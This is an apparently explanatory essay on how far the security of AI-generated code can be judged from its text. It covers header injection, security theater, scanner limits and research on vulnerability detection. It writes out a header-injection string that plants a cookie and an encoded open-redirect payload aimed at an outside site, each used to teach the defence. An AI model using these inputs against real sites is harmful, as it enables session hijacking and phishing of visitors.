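# Judging the Security of AI-Written Code from Its Text

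## What makes code secure, and what security theater looks like

AI-generated code is program text that a large language model (LLM) writes in response to a request in ordinary language. Programmers now use LLMs routinely, and much of the resulting code runs and does what they asked for. It is harder to tell whether the code is also secure. *CWEval* (Peng, Cui et al., 2025) points out that people easily spot and discard code that doesn't work, but often miss security faults in working code, especially if they aren't security specialists. How well can a careful reader find such faults from the text of the code, and what other evidence is needed when reading isn't enough?

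### One function, one attack

When a browser requests a page, the web server's response starts with headers. Each header has a name and a value and sits on its own line, which ends with two invisible characters, a carriage return and a line feed, that programmers write as `\r\n`. The Python function below sets the header for the page's language.

```python
def set_language(headers, value):
    # Security: validate untrusted input before it reaches the response
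    if not isinstance(value, str):
        raise TypeError("Header value must be a string")
    logger.info("Setting Content-Language header")
    headers["Content-Language"] = value
```

It reads well. There is a check, an error message, an entry in the log and a comment about security. Suppose that the site takes the value from the visitor's request and that the server copies it into the response unchanged. A visitor who sends `fr` gets a header for French. An attacker sends this instead:

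```python
"fr\r\nSet-Cookie: session=attacker123"
```

The response now contains two headers where the programmer wanted one:

```
Content-Language: fr
Set-Cookie: session=attacker123
```

The browser stores a cookie of the attacker's choosing. If the value travels in a link, the attacker only has to get somebody else to click it. Worse is possible with more line breaks: MITRE's *CWE-113*, the reference entry for this weakness, shows an attacker ending the response early and writing a whole second one, which a shared cache may then hand to other visitors. The type check is no help, because the attack string is a string. One line before the assignment closes the hole:

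```python
    if "\r" in value or "\n" in value: raise ValueError("Line break in header value")
```

LLMs do write code of this build. Santos de Moura, Matuschek and colleagues (2026), in *Newer and Bigger, but Safer?*, read samples from a header task and found that the programs check the header's type carefully and then assign the value with its line breaks intact, a mistake close to universal among the 32 models in the study. (The function above at least logs a fixed message. Had it logged the raw value, the same line break would have let the attacker forge log entries, which is a weakness of its own, CWE-117.)

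### The working vocabulary

The hole in `set_language` is a *vulnerability*, a fault that lets an attacker make a program do something its owner forbids. Here, the attacker can plant cookies in other people's browsers. The numbers come from the Common Weakness Enumeration (*CWE*), a catalogue of weakness types that the American non-profit MITRE maintains. CWE-113 means header injection in any program. OpenSSF's *Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE)* explains that a single publicly known flaw in a single product gets a CVE number instead.

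MITRE's *CWE Glossary* distinguishes a weakness from a vulnerability, defining a weakness as a condition that could contribute to a vulnerability "under certain circumstances". A *threat model* records those circumstances: what the owner wants to protect, from whom, and what the attacker is able to do. For the header function, the goal might be to protect visitors' sessions from anyone who can send the site a request but cannot log in to the server. A different threat model can change the verdict. If the value comes only from a settings file that the owner writes, no attacker can reach it, and the same six lines are harmless.

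*Static analysis* means examining code without running it, and a tool that does this is a scanner. To find CWE-113, a scanner typically traces data from a source, such as a request parameter, to a sink, such as a response header, and looks for vulnerable patterns along the way. Scanners can miss vulnerabilities, and a vulnerable program that an assessment passes as clean is called a *false negative*. Peng and colleagues give an example from CodeQL, a widely used scanner. One of its rules looks for a few known bad ways of checking a web address, and it catches two vulnerable programs but passes two others that differ only slightly.

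Running the code gives another kind of evidence. A *functional test* checks whether the program does what the programmer asked for, such as producing `Content-Language: fr` when given `fr`. An *attack test* runs the program on hostile input and checks whether a particular attack succeeds. For example, it might pass in the string with the cookie and look for a second header. A test's *oracle* is whatever decides its result. For the header attack, the oracle could be a rule that exactly one header comes out. For an attack that ties up the server with endless work, Peng and colleagues use a time limit.

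An evaluation needs both functional and security tests, because it is easy to make code secure if it doesn't have to work. *Secure and Functional Code Generation with Self-Evaluation* (Al Mamun and Uddin, 2026) shows three versions of a header function that one model wrote under different instructions. One is a plain assignment, which works but is open to attack. Another accepts only a single language tag such as `en-US`, which keeps out line breaks but also rejects `en-US, en; q=0.9`, a legal value. The third adds a short check for `\r` and `\n`, and is the only version that both works and stops the attack.

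### Security theater

The type check in `set_language` runs on every call but does nothing to stop this attack. Measures like this are called security theater. Popik's *Security Theater*, a history of the phrase, traces it to *Beyond Fear* (2003), in which the security technologist Bruce Schneier wrote that some countermeasures "provide the feeling of security instead of the reality". Schneier's examples come mostly from buildings and airports. In *Beyond Security Theater*, Schneier (2009) mentions office guards who check photo IDs, though nobody has explained how knowing that a visitor has one protects anyone. He also mentions the National Guard troops who stood in American airports after September 11 with no bullets in their guns.

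Security theater doesn't require anyone to know that it is a show, although the word "theater" suggests it does. On Schneier's account, frightened people want somebody to do something, politicians want to oblige, and a useless measure follows without anyone having to lie. *In Praise of Security Theater* even defends one example, radio-tagged bracelets meant to prevent baby abduction, which comfort mothers whose fear is larger than the danger.

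Honest misunderstanding is enough to produce security theater in code. *Assessing the Software Security Comprehension of Large Language Models* (2025) records LLMs recommending defences as much more effective than they are. One was to use an object-relational mapping, a library that builds database queries for the programmer, as a complete cure for SQL injection, in which an attacker puts database commands into ordinary input. But such libraries commonly let a programmer paste raw text into a query, which makes injection possible again. Another was to stop cross-site request forgery, where a hostile page makes a visitor's browser act on a site the visitor has logged in to, by accepting only POST requests, the type that web forms use. A hostile page can send a POST request too. Students who have finished security courses hold similar mistaken beliefs, for instance that encryption solves everything.

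Security theater in code is a visible security measure that gives a feeling of safety but does little or nothing to stop an attack, whether or not anyone meant to deceive. The label depends on the threat model. According to a summary of *Beyond Fear*, Schneier judges any security measure partly by how well it mitigates the risks to the things one is trying to protect. The type check is good programming because it catches a caller who passes in a number by mistake, but it does nothing to stop header injection, the attack that matters here. It is theater because the comment above it presents it as a security measure.

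### Missing, idle and misplaced defences

Insecure code may have no defence, a defence that does nothing, or a sound defence in the wrong place. These problems look quite different in the text.

If `set_language` contained only its last line, it would have no defence. MITRE calls a protective step "missing" when the developer hasn't attempted it, as in that case, and "incorrect" when the developer attempts it and gets it wrong. The function as printed, including its comment, belongs under "incorrect" because whoever wrote it tried to validate the input but checked the wrong property.

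For a misplaced defence, change the last line to this:

```python
    headers["Content-Language"] = html.escape(value)
```

Python's standard `html.escape` function escapes characters such as `<` that have a special meaning in a web page. It is a sound defence against script injection where text enters a page, but it doesn't protect a header from inserted line breaks because it leaves `\r\n` unchanged. MITRE notes that an element that is special in one representation may not be special in another; a space, for example, separates arguments in a command shell but not in the body of a web page. A check can also run at the wrong time. Line breaks are often encoded as `%0d%0a`, and an otherwise correct check for `\r` and `\n` misses them if it runs before the program decodes the value. MITRE therefore advises developers to decode input before validating it.

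Idle and misplaced defences can overlap. For example, a misplaced escaping function in a header is also idle there, because it doesn't protect the header. The distinction is still useful because moving a misplaced defence can make it work, while a type check won't stop a line break no matter where it is placed.

Idle defences are the hardest of these to see. A reviewer who asks whether anything validates the input will find nothing in the bare version and start to worry. The reviewer can find a misplaced defence by following the value to where it ends up, although that may mean following it through the whole program. But an idle defence looks like validation because it uses the same words as a working one, such as "validate", "untrusted", `if not` and `raise`. The useless check and the line that fixes the function also have the same grammar, a condition and then an error. To tell them apart,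 the reviewer has to ask which hostile string the check would reject, not just whether there is a check, and this requires having the attack in mind already.

Ordinary testing won't expose it either. Functional tests use the values that ordinary users send, and no ordinary language tag contains a line break. Tests on such values pass with the type check, without it, and with the real fix, so they can't distinguish these versions. For each task in their benchmark, Peng and colleagues wrote at least one version that passes every functional test and fails a security test. *False Security Confidence in Benign LLM Code Generation* (2026) defines a sample *s* as showing "False Security Confidence" when FCR(*s*) = 1 and SSR(*s*) = 0, meaning that it passes the functional correctness check and fails the security check. The worry is that people will over-trust such code because it works. The definition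 is broader than security theater, since it covers the bare assignment as well as the version with the comforting comment, and both would get the same test results.

### Three meanings of "text alone"

Asking whether someone can judge security "from the text alone" runs together three questions with different answers.

A reader can't tell from the text of `set_language` who supplies `value`, whether an earlier step has removed its line breaks, or what `headers` is. If `headers` is a plain dictionary that the server later writes out unchanged, the attack works. If it is an object from a library that refuses line breaks, the attack fails and the function is safe without a fix. A reader can't assume that a well-known library refuses them, either. Larson (2026), in *wsgiref.headers.Headers allows header newline injection*, announced that a header class in Python's standard library let line breaks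 in user-controlled values inject headers. The same function could therefore be vulnerable on an affected version of Python and safe on a repaired one.

A reader who has the whole source can see the function's callers and any filter between the request and the header, which resolves many doubts about the function. But the source may not show which version of Python the server runs or what stands in front of it. MITRE lists load balancers, proxies, caches and application firewalls among the components that have to keep a consistent view of HTTP traffic, and the poisoned-cache attack requires a cache. The source may also show that any logged-in user can read every invoice without showing whether the owner intended that.

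Reading is most effective for judging code when the reader has the source, a specification of what the owner forbids, and deployment settings that give the versions and the surrounding machinery. An expert or a proof tool can establish a lot from these, but their conclusions still depend on the description of the surroundings being true. *SoK* (2024), a survey of guarantees in software security, gives the example of seL4, an operating-system kernel. Researchers proved mathematically that information flows in seL4 only where its policy permits, but five years later the Spectre flaw in the underlying processor broke that property.

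People who disagree about whether you can judge code's security by reading it may be thinking of different kinds of code. Someone who thinks of a function with an unguarded header and a known caller will say you can, while someone who thinks of a fragment pasted into a chat window has good reason to say you can't.

### One attack refutes, no number of failures establishes

Even if the evaluator can run the program as well as read it, insecurity is still easier to demonstrate than security. A program is secure if no input that the threat model lets an attacker send can make it do something the owner forbids. A single input that does so disproves the claim that the program is secure, and anyone can rerun it to check. Testing a thousand harmless inputs doesn't prove the claim, because other inputs remain untested, and if inputs can be strings of any length, no finite set of tests can cover them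 all.

Suppose the programmer tries to fix this by rejecting values that contain the pair `\r\n`. The earlier attack string now fails, and so does every variation that uses the pair. But some programs that read HTTP accept a lone `\n` as the end of a line, so an attack that uses `\n` alone still works against them. The attack tests showed only that the strings they tried were blocked.

Herley (2016), in *Unfalsifiability of security claims*, makes the point more generally. A break-in shows that a system is insecure, but no observation shows that an arbitrary system is secure, because the claim covers an unlimited future and a year without a break-in doesn't rule out one the year after. Herley draws a consequence that bears directly on security theater: no observation can refute the claim that a given measure is necessary, because that would require identifying a secure system that lacks it.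 Countermeasures therefore accumulate as new attacks appear. An attack test can show that the type check is not *enough* to protect the header, but it can't show that deleting the check would be safe, so a cautious maintainer will probably leave both the check and its comment in place.

Reasoning can sometimes establish what testing cannot. With the one-line fix in place, a reader can see that no string containing `\r` or `\n` reaches the assignment, without having to test every string. But concluding that no attacker can inject a header also requires assuming that nothing downstream treats any other character as a line break. Herley observes that every formal proof of security starts from assumptions about what an attacker can and cannot do. A successful attack will expose a wrong assumption about what attackers cannot do, but only after it has happened.

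Failed attacks are still useful evidence. Schneier (2003), in *Beyond Fear*, calls testing security both impossible and essential, which is about right. A program that has withstood capable attackers deserves more trust than one that nobody has tried to break. How much more trust it deserves depends on who attacked it, what access they had and when they tried. *LLMs + Security = Trouble* (2026) stresses the date. Exploitable paths through a program are rare, and AI checkers and attackers cover only some of them, so code that withstands today's models may be broken by the models in use a year from now.

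## Judging a single function without the rest of the program

A reader of `set_language` can't tell whether an attacker supplies the value, because that depends on code elsewhere in the program. Risse, Liu and Böhme (2024), in *Top Score on the Wrong Exam*, surveyed the 81 papers on finding vulnerabilities with machine learning that leading software-engineering and security venues published from 2020 to 2024. In 88% of them, the task was nevertheless to decide whether a single function contains a vulnerability without seeing any other code. The researchers then checked how often this was possible.

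### A division by zero that depends on the caller

Their opening example comes from TensorFlow Lite, a machine-learning library. The function splits an array into equal parts. With simpler names and only the lines that matter, it looks like this:

```c
int resize_outputs(int input_size, int num_splits) {
    if (input_size % num_splits != 0)
        return ERROR_UNEVEN_SPLIT;
    int slice_size = input_size / num_splits;
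    /* ... give each output slice_size elements ... */
}
```

The `%` operator gives the remainder of a division. If `input_size` is 12 and `num_splits` is 4, the remainder is 0 and each output gets 3 elements. If `num_splits` is 5, the remainder is 2 and the function returns an error. If `num_splits` is 0, the program divides by zero and crashes. The crash happens inside the validation check, so a reviewer who looks for validation will still find some.

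Whether an attacker can cause the crash depends on the callers. Suppose only one function calls `resize_outputs`, and it rejects any number of splits below 1. Then `num_splits` is never zero and the code is safe. But if a second caller reads the number from an uploaded file, a stranger can crash the program by putting 0 in that file, even though the code of `resize_outputs` hasn't changed. The flaw in the real function is listed as CVE-2021-29599.

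Risse and colleagues call such a vulnerability *context-dependent*, meaning that the code is vulnerable or safe only because of something outside it. It is reasonable to advise programmers to have each function check its own arguments, but a program that checks a value once, when it enters the program, and trusts it afterwards isn't vulnerable. A reviewer who flags every unchecked argument will flag a great deal of sound C code.

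### What two experts could decide

For the main study, Risse and colleagues randomly drew 300 functions labelled "vulnerable", 100 from each of three widely used collections, BigVul, Devign and DiverseVul. When a commit (a recorded change to a project's code) fixes a vulnerability, these collections label the earlier version of every function it changed as vulnerable.

This rule can mislabel functions. *VulValidate* (Zhang and Chen, 2026) describes a commit to the compression library zstd that added a missing size check to one function and only logging calls to three others. BigVul labels all four vulnerable. So two security researchers on the Risse team first read each function alongside its patch and any CVE report to decide whether it had caused a vulnerability. The labelling took more than 150 hours and left 151 functions: 39 from BigVul, 47 from Devign and 65 from DiverseVul.

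The two researchers then considered whether a reader could identify each vulnerability from the function's own code, and concluded that this was not possible for any of the 151. Working independently, they agreed on 82% of functions in the first round and 98% in the second, and they settled the rest by discussion.

They also took 90 functions labeled "secure", 30 from each collection, and tried to think of a context that would make each one vulnerable. They succeeded for 82. For instance, they wrote a small artificial program that makes one function from the web cache Varnish follow a null pointer, an address that points to nothing.

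The result for secure functions is weaker than it sounds, because C doesn't stop a caller from passing a bad pointer. Almost any function that uses a pointer will crash for some imaginable caller, and people don't normally require functions to prevent this. The result still means that a reader can't separate vulnerable functions from secure ones by asking whether something could go wrong, since in both groups something nearly always could.

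### Most of the missing context was text

For each of the 151 functions, Risse and colleagues recorded what a reader would have needed to judge it. Each range below gives the lowest and highest values among the three collections.

| What the reader lacked | Share of functions | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Code of a function that this one calls | 43–52% | A buffer overflow that depends on what a lookup function can return |
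| Values that callers pass in | 40–47% | The division by zero above |
| Global variables and macros | 2–10% | A buffer whose size depends on whether a macro is defined |
| Type declarations | 0–3% | An integer overflow that depends on the size of a menu item |
| Execution environment | 0–3% | A fault that needs a certain file to exist on the user's machine |

Apart from the execution environment, all of this is normally text in the same project or in a library it uses, though build settings may decide whether a macro is defined. The study is therefore strong evidence against judging snippets and much weaker evidence against reading a whole repository. It also doesn't show that reading the repository works, because the two labellers had the patch, which told them where to look.

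In *VulContextBench*, Li, Jiang and colleagues (2026) measured how much code from outside a change helps a model find a vulnerability in it. They collected 111 commits that introduced vulnerabilities into projects in five programming languages. For each commit, an annotator marked the code a reader needs in order to see the problem, such as the route from an attacker's input to the changed lines. OpenAI's GPT-5.5 identified the vulnerability in 27.0% of attempts when given only the change, and in 75.1% when also given the marked code.

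This large gain came entirely from text. But the annotator knew the answer while choosing the passages, and finding the right few pages in a large repository is a good part of the task. When seven models had to search the repositories themselves, they opened between 73% and 92% of the marked code, depending on the model, but cited only 9% to 36% of it as evidence in their final reports.

### High scores from counting words

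Many detectors scored well even though a function's text rarely settles whether it is secure. Risse and colleagues tested one explanation by training a simple classifier only on how often each word occurred in a function. The classifier used gradient boosting, a standard method that adds up many small decision trees. A check placed before a division gives the same word counts as the same check placed after it, so the classifier could not tell whether a defence worked. Training and testing took 30 minutes on a laptop.

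The usual score in this field is F1, the harmonic mean of the share of flagged functions that are vulnerable and the share of vulnerable functions that the detector flags. A perfect detector scores 1. For comparison, the last column below lists the F1 of a detector that flags every function, which is 2*p*/(1 + *p*) when a proportion *p* of the functions is vulnerable.

| Collection | Leading method | Word counts only | Flagging everything |
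|---|---|---|---|
| BigVul | 0.96 | 0.86 | about 0.09 |
| Devign | 0.68 | 0.62 | about 0.65 |
| DiverseVul | 0.48 | 0.11 | about 0.10 |

Fewer than one in twenty functions in BigVul are labeled "vulnerable", yet a classifier that sees only word counts can identify most of them without learning how the code behaves.

The Devign result needs more care, because nearly half of that collection is labelled vulnerable and even the leading method barely beats flagging everything. Accuracy is more informative here. Word counts reach 63% and the leading method 68%, while calling every function secure would get about 52%. On DiverseVul the word counts were almost no use, so they can't account for the leading method's 0.48. Risse and colleagues showed that a program can get high scores on some of these collections without detecting vulnerabilities, but they are careful not to treat this as proof that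 the leading methods get their scores that way. There is some direct evidence that detectors do. According to *The Data Problem in Software Vulnerability Analysis* (2026), a review of the field's data, an earlier study found detectors relying on particular variable and function names.

One way to remove such shortcuts is to test a detector on the same function before and after its fix. The two versions share nearly all their words, and the detector gets credit only if it flags the old one and clears the new one. Cichoń and Dmitruk (2026), in *A Function-Level Vulnerability Score Measures Flag Rate More Than the Model*, ran 68 language models on such pairs. Seven of them, including Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.2, got 6% to 25% of pairs right, depending on the model and the benchmark. On the largest set, GPT-5.2 flagged both versions in 82% of pairs. Of the 68 models, 64 gave both versions the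 same answer more often than independent guesses would have. Their verdicts mostly depended on the text the two versions shared rather than on the fix.

Cichoń and Dmitruk also found some signal in the function's text. They trained a simple classifier on the internal activations of six open models, and it ranked the vulnerable version above the fixed one in 78% of pairs of similar length, compared with 64% using word frequencies. The signal seems to come from code that patches add, such as an extra check. This is compatible with the result of Risse and colleagues, because telling which of two versions came after a fix is much easier than telling whether a single function is vulnerable.

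### Is it really none?

Zero out of 151 is a surprising result, and the main doubts about it concern what the labellers counted as context and where the functions came from. Sample size is a smaller concern. If one in fifty functions of this kind could be judged alone, a random sample of 151 would contain none of them only about 5% of the time.

The labellers were among the paper's authors, and they expected to find context dependence. When a check could have gone in either a function or its caller, they counted only the called function as vulnerable. This rule guarantees that such a function's vulnerability depends on its caller. Their 98% agreement shows that they applied the rule consistently, but not that the rule was right.

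The rule also strictly limits what a reader is allowed to know. *VULPO* (2025) gives an example from Linux, CVE-2025-21982, where a function uses the result of `devm_kasprintf()` without checking whether it is null. A small language model that saw only this function called it safe, because nothing in it shows that the result can be null. A kernel developer may well know that it can, so an experienced reader can sometimes supply context that the text lacks.

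Zhang and Chen independently checked the first round of labelling with an AI agent that rebuilt old versions of the programs, attacked the functions, and compared their behaviour before and after each patch. Where both the agent and Risse and colleagues reached a decision, they agreed on 71 of 92 functions from BigVul and 68 of 87 from DiverseVul. In 17 of the 21 BigVul disagreements, the agent confirmed a defect in a function that the human labellers had called secure. Those functions never reached the second round, so nobody knows whether a reader could have judged them without the rest of the program.

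In *Graph Is the Verifier*, Li, Zhang and colleagues (2026) report a lower figure. They had Claude Opus 4.8 judge 138 vulnerable functions and found that 99 of them, or 71.7%, needed evidence from outside the function. But the model had a summary of the confirmed defect, and a fault looks more obvious once it has been explained, so the true figure for C code of this kind is probably between their 72% and the 100% reported by Risse and colleagues.

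Other kinds of code may be easier to judge one function at a time. The three collections consist mainly of C, where functions constantly receive pointers and sizes from elsewhere, and the Devign sample came from two projects. A short web handler in Python may read a request parameter and paste it into a database query within five lines, which gives a reader good grounds to reject the code without seeing a caller. Even so, Wang and Huang (2026) point out in *Security Is Relative* that the same pattern is secure in a project that reliably cleans all input before it reaches that code.

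Researchers still label AI-written code one function at a time. *LLMVul* (2026) is a collection of C and C++ functions written by language models and taken from production repositories. Three scanners voted on each function. Human raters then checked 100 of the functions, seeing only the function and the suspected type of weakness. If even the lower estimate applies to these functions, the raters often lacked the information they needed to decide.

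### Supplying the context

Simply pasting the surrounding code into a detector's input doesn't help much. In *Beyond Function-Level Analysis*, Li, Zhang and colleagues (2026) added callers, called functions and global variables to the input of two established code models, and accuracy fell slightly on all three of their datasets. On PrimeVul, a more carefully labelled collection, the better model's accuracy fell from 56.65% to 54.22%; guessing gets 50%.

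Their own system, CPRVul, uses a language model to summarise each piece of context and select the most relevant ones. A second model, trained on written explanations of known vulnerabilities, reasons about the function together with the selected context. CPRVul reached 67.78% on PrimeVul. The gain over 56.65% isn't due to context alone, because the two figures come from different models. Removing the summarising and selecting step lowered the score by only 2.36 points, while removing the reasoning step lowered it by 15.24. The largest improvement was for faults in permissions and access control, from 52% to 79% on 48 functions, which makes sense if the missing check tends to be in another function.

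Another approach lets the detector look up information about the rest of the program. Li and colleagues, in *Graph Is the Verifier*, trained a small model to query a map of the program for callers, called functions and the paths that data takes. During training, they rewarded it partly for citing the right evidence. The model judged both versions correctly in 37.8% of PrimeVul pairs, against 27.3% for Claude Opus 4.7. This is progress, but it still misjudged at least one version in most pairs.

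Wang and Huang got much further, with 64.4% of pairs correct, by supplying a different kind of context. Their system, Phoenix, uses the vulnerable version, the fix and the CVE description to derive a requirement the function must meet, and then has a model check whether the code meets it. The result shows how useful a precise specification would be to a reader who had one, but it doesn't show that this method can find vulnerabilities in new code, which has no fix to derive the requirement from.

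*Vulnerability Detection with Interprocedural Context in Multiple Languages* (Lira, Fonseca and colleagues, 2026) tested models only on vulnerable functions, so a model that always answered "vulnerable" would have scored 100%. Its results therefore only seem to contradict the points above. Claude Haiku 4.5 flagged about 98% of the functions from the code alone, and adding callers or called functions made almost no difference. GPT-4.1 Mini dropped from 74% to 54% when it also saw the called functions, but without safe functions in the test, we can't tell whether it got worse at detecting vulnerabilities or just more cautious about flagging code.

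The researchers checked a sample of the explanations that the models had written from the function alone, and Haiku had correctly identified and explained the known vulnerability in 93.6% of cases. A model can evidently point to the weak spot in a function without seeing its callers, at least for vulnerabilities that are already public. This test couldn't show whether it would also invent equally convincing weak spots in safe functions.

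### Reporting the condition

Risse and colleagues suggested that a detector could instead state the condition under which a function would be vulnerable, and somebody could then check whether the real program meets it. For `resize_outputs`, the detector would report that the program crashes if any caller can pass zero, which is true whoever the callers are.

Liu and Böhme (2026), in *LLM-based Code Auditing by Inferring and Evaluating Developer Assumptions*, built CREED, a tool that works this way. It prompts a language model to state what a function does, what its developer must have assumed, whether each assumption is reasonable and when it would fail. One of their examples is a sign-in function that returns the same error for an unknown user and for a wrong password, a standard way to stop attackers from learning which accounts exist. But the function computes a password hash only if the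 user exists, so the error takes longer to return for a wrong password, and an attacker who measures response times can still learn which accounts exist. CREED found this flaw, CVE-2026-25222, and the four tools it was compared with missed it.

Liu and Böhme tested CREED on 50 functions from recent CVEs in ten programming languages, after confirming by hand that each function contained the root cause. CREED explained the known vulnerability in 39 of them. In 33 cases it also stopped reporting the vulnerability when given the fixed version. But it produced 310 findings in total, or 7.9 for every known vulnerability it found.

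Liu and Böhme inspected the first finding for each function and judged 37 of the 50 to be genuine vulnerabilities, including 14 that they hadn't been looking for. Ten of the 13 false alarms stated the condition correctly, but a caller or a protective function elsewhere kept it from arising. Somebody still has to check whether the rest of the code allows the condition, as they do when a solver outputs a crashing input without specifying the caller.

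Sometimes even the rest of the code isn't enough to judge whether a function is secure. CREED missed CVE-2026-32761, in which a user without permission to download a file could still share it. The function checked for permission to share, which looks sufficient if you don't know that the application's owner also requires permission to download.

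## Code that passes static analysis and can still be attacked

A person often has to search one file at a time to find what calls a function, while a scanner can apply the same rules to every line of a repository in seconds. Companies therefore often require a clean scan before they release code, and researchers use scanners to grade the code that LLMs write. The value of a clean scan depends on what the scanner looks for.

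### From patterns to taint tracking

The simplest rules describe a piece of bad code. The scanner parses the program into a tree and searches it for nodes that match a rule. A function call, for example, is a node with the function's name and arguments attached, and a rule against the outdated hash function MD5 might match every call to `hashlib.md5`. CodeQL uses a richer structure. According to *GitHub’s Copilot Code Review* (2025), it builds a graph of the code's meaning, and its rules are logical queries on that graph.

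A pattern rule catches only the mistakes its author thought of, as with CodeQL's rule for badly checked web addresses.

Header injection happens when text from a request parameter reaches a header with its line breaks intact. It doesn't fit a single pattern, because reading a parameter and setting a header are each harmless on their own. Scanners find faults like this by *taint tracking*, which traces data from a source (here, the request parameter) to a sink (the header). Semgrep, a widely used scanner, treats data from a source as tainted and follows it through assignments and function calls. A sanitizer, an operation that checks or cleans the data, removes the taint, and Semgrep reports data only if it is still tainted at a sink. Semgrep's *Taint analysis* explains that rule writers specify the sources, sinks and sanitizers as lists of code patterns.

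Consider these three lines:

```python
lang = request.args["lang"]
value = html.escape(lang)
headers["Content-Language"] = value
```

Suppose a rule lists `request.args` as a source, an assignment to `headers` as a sink and `html.escape` as a sanitizer. The scanner marks `lang` as tainted on the first line. On the second line it finds `html.escape` and marks `value` as clean, so it reports nothing when `value` reaches the sink. But `html.escape` doesn't remove line breaks, so the attack string with the extra cookie still works.

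The scanner matched the sanitizer's name but did not check what the function does to a line break. Semgrep's *Taint mode is now in beta* has an example in which this shortcut is reasonable, because the sinks insert text into a web page and the listed sanitizer, `$sanitize()`, is meant to clean text for that use. A careful rule author would leave `html.escape` off the list for headers. But most large projects also have their own cleaning functions, with names like `clean_input`. If nobody lists such a function, the scanner may raise an alarm every time data passes through it, even where the function works. If somebody lists it to stop these alarms, the scanner treats its output as safe at every sink the rule covers.

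Taint tracking handles a defence that does nothing better than a misplaced one. If the middle line were the type check from `set_language`, the value would stay tainted, because no sensible rule lists `isinstance` as a sanitizer. The scanner would report the hole, regardless of the comment about security. A scanner does better here than a hurried reviewer, provided its analysis includes the source of the value. Semgrep's documentation describes the analysis as following data through the body of one function, and in `set_language` the value arrives as an argument. A rule can treat every argument as a source, but then the scanner will also flag functions whose callers pass only safe values.

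### A check that comes too early

Even the right check in the right function can fail. OpenAI's *Why Codex Security Doesn’t Include a SAST Report* (2026) gives the example of a web application that checks a redirect address against a pattern, decodes it and then sends the visitor there. (SAST, static application security testing, is the industry's name for this kind of scanning.) A short version might look like this:

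```python
if re.match(r"/[^/]", target):   # one slash: a page on this site
    redirect(unquote(target))
```

The pattern requires a slash followed by a character other than a slash. An attacker sends `/%2Fevil.example`, which passes because the second character is a percent sign. Decoding turns it into `//evil.example`, and a browser treats an address that starts with two slashes as a link to another site. The attacker can send people a link that starts at a site they trust and ends at a copy of its login page.

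If the scanner counts the pattern check as a sanitizer, it misses this attack, which works because the program checks the address before decoding it. Otherwise, it also flags the safe version, which decodes the address first. To tell the two versions apart, the scanner would have to determine which strings pass the check and how decoding changes them. The web framework Express had a flaw of this kind, CVE-2024-29041, in which malformed addresses got past common lists of permitted sites.

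OpenAI claims in its post that the hardest vulnerabilities usually aren't about where data flows. It has an interest in this claim because it sells an AI reviewer that competes with scanners, and the post includes no count to support "usually". But the explanation of the mechanism is sound, and anyone can check the example by hand.

### What Rice's theorem rules out

Better rules would fix some of these misses, but a theorem that the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953 shows that no set of rules could fix them all. The theorem covers any property that depends only on what a program does, so that two programs with the same outputs for the same inputs either both have it or both lack it. If some programs have such a property and others don't, no algorithm can decide correctly, for every program, whether it has the property.

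The idea behind the proof fits in three lines of Python:

```python
def respond(request, headers):
    p()
    headers["Content-Language"] = request.args["lang"]
```

Let `p` be any program that takes no input and only calculates. An attacker can inject a header exactly when `p` eventually stops, because the last line runs only then. A scanner that was always right about header injection could therefore determine, for every `p`, whether it stops. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can do that.

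So no scanner for header injection can be fully automatic, always right and applicable to every program. Tool builders have to give up at least one of these properties. A scanner may miss some vulnerable programs, flag some safe ones, or return "don't know". It may accept only programs in a restricted language, such as one where every loop has a fixed limit. Or a person may help with the reasoning, as researchers did when they proved properties of seL4.

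Rice's theorem doesn't prevent us from telling whether a particular program is secure. For example, once `set_language` has its one-line fix, a short argument shows that no line break gets past the check. The theorem also doesn't determine how often a scanner will be wrong. It is consistent with a tool that errs on one program in a billion and with one that misses half of all vulnerabilities. Some misses have nothing to do with the theorem, such as when a scanner overlooks a weak password hash because nobody wrote a rule for it.

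The theoretical limit also applies to AI reviewers and automatic attackers, because they are algorithms too. Scanners have practical limits as well. OpenAI points out that they approximate in order to finish in reasonable time on large programs, especially where the code chooses which function to call only while it is running.

### Attacking the files that scanners passed

In *Beyond Static Guarantees*, Pourleyli, Urmi and Melo (2026) tried to measure how often code with a clean scan is open to attack. They collected 1,355 Python files from three security datasets and ran two free scanners on them, Semgrep and the Python-specific Bandit. They removed the 701 files in which either scanner reported anything, however minor, which left 654 clean ones.

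An AI agent built on OpenAI's small model GPT-5.4 nano then read each clean file and looked for weaknesses. Before reporting a weakness, it had to look up MITRE's definition of it. The agent examined every file five times, and a weakness counted only if the agent reported it at least three times. This produced 394 suspected vulnerabilities in 235 files, counting each pair of a file and a CWE number as one vulnerability.

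A second agent, built on the same model, tried to exploit each of the 394 suspected weaknesses by writing attack programs and running them in an isolated container with no network connection. A crash counted only if crashing was the suspected weakness. A path traversal, for example, had to reach a file outside the permitted folder. Again there were five runs, and at least three had to succeed. The agent confirmed 120 of the weaknesses and partly confirmed another 20. It couldn't trigger 208, and the remaining 46 were inconclusive.

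The study calls its main measure the Static-Pass Dynamic-Fail Rate:

SPDFR = |static-pass ∩ dynamic-fail| / |static-pass|

Both scanners passed 654 files, and the agent then exploited 83 of them (12.69%). Those 83 files contained the 120 confirmed vulnerabilities. Including partly confirmed cases raises the count to 95 files (14.53%).

Five kinds of weakness with confirmed attacks never appeared in either scanner's output, for any of the 1,355 files:

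| Weakness | Confirmed cases |
|---|---|
| Random numbers from a generator unfit for cryptography (CWE-338) | 15 |
| Password hashes that are too quick to compute (CWE-916) | 9 |
| File names or paths under outside control (CWE-73) | 6 |
| No limit on the resources a user can claim (CWE-770) | 6 |
| No check that the user has permission (CWE-862) | 6 |

Together they make up 42 of the 120 confirmations. Some of these gaps may be smaller than they look, because the comparison is by CWE number. In MITRE's catalogue, CWE-338 is a special case of CWE-330, insufficiently random values, and Bandit did report CWE-330 in other files. The missing permission check is a more serious gap, because a scanner can't detect that a check is missing unless somebody has told it which actions need permission.

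The two scanners took 77 seconds to check the whole collection. The agents took 28.7 hours, or about 20 minutes for each file they exploited, and used 96.3 million tokens (roughly, the word fragments that language models read and write).

### How far to trust the 12.69%

Most of the confirmations came from one collection:

| Collection | Files | Suspected | Confirmed |
|---|---|---|---|
| RedCode | 810 | 315 | 106 (33.7%) |
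| CyberNative | 424 | 42 | 12 (28.6%) |
| SecurityEval | 121 | 37 | 2 (5.4%) |

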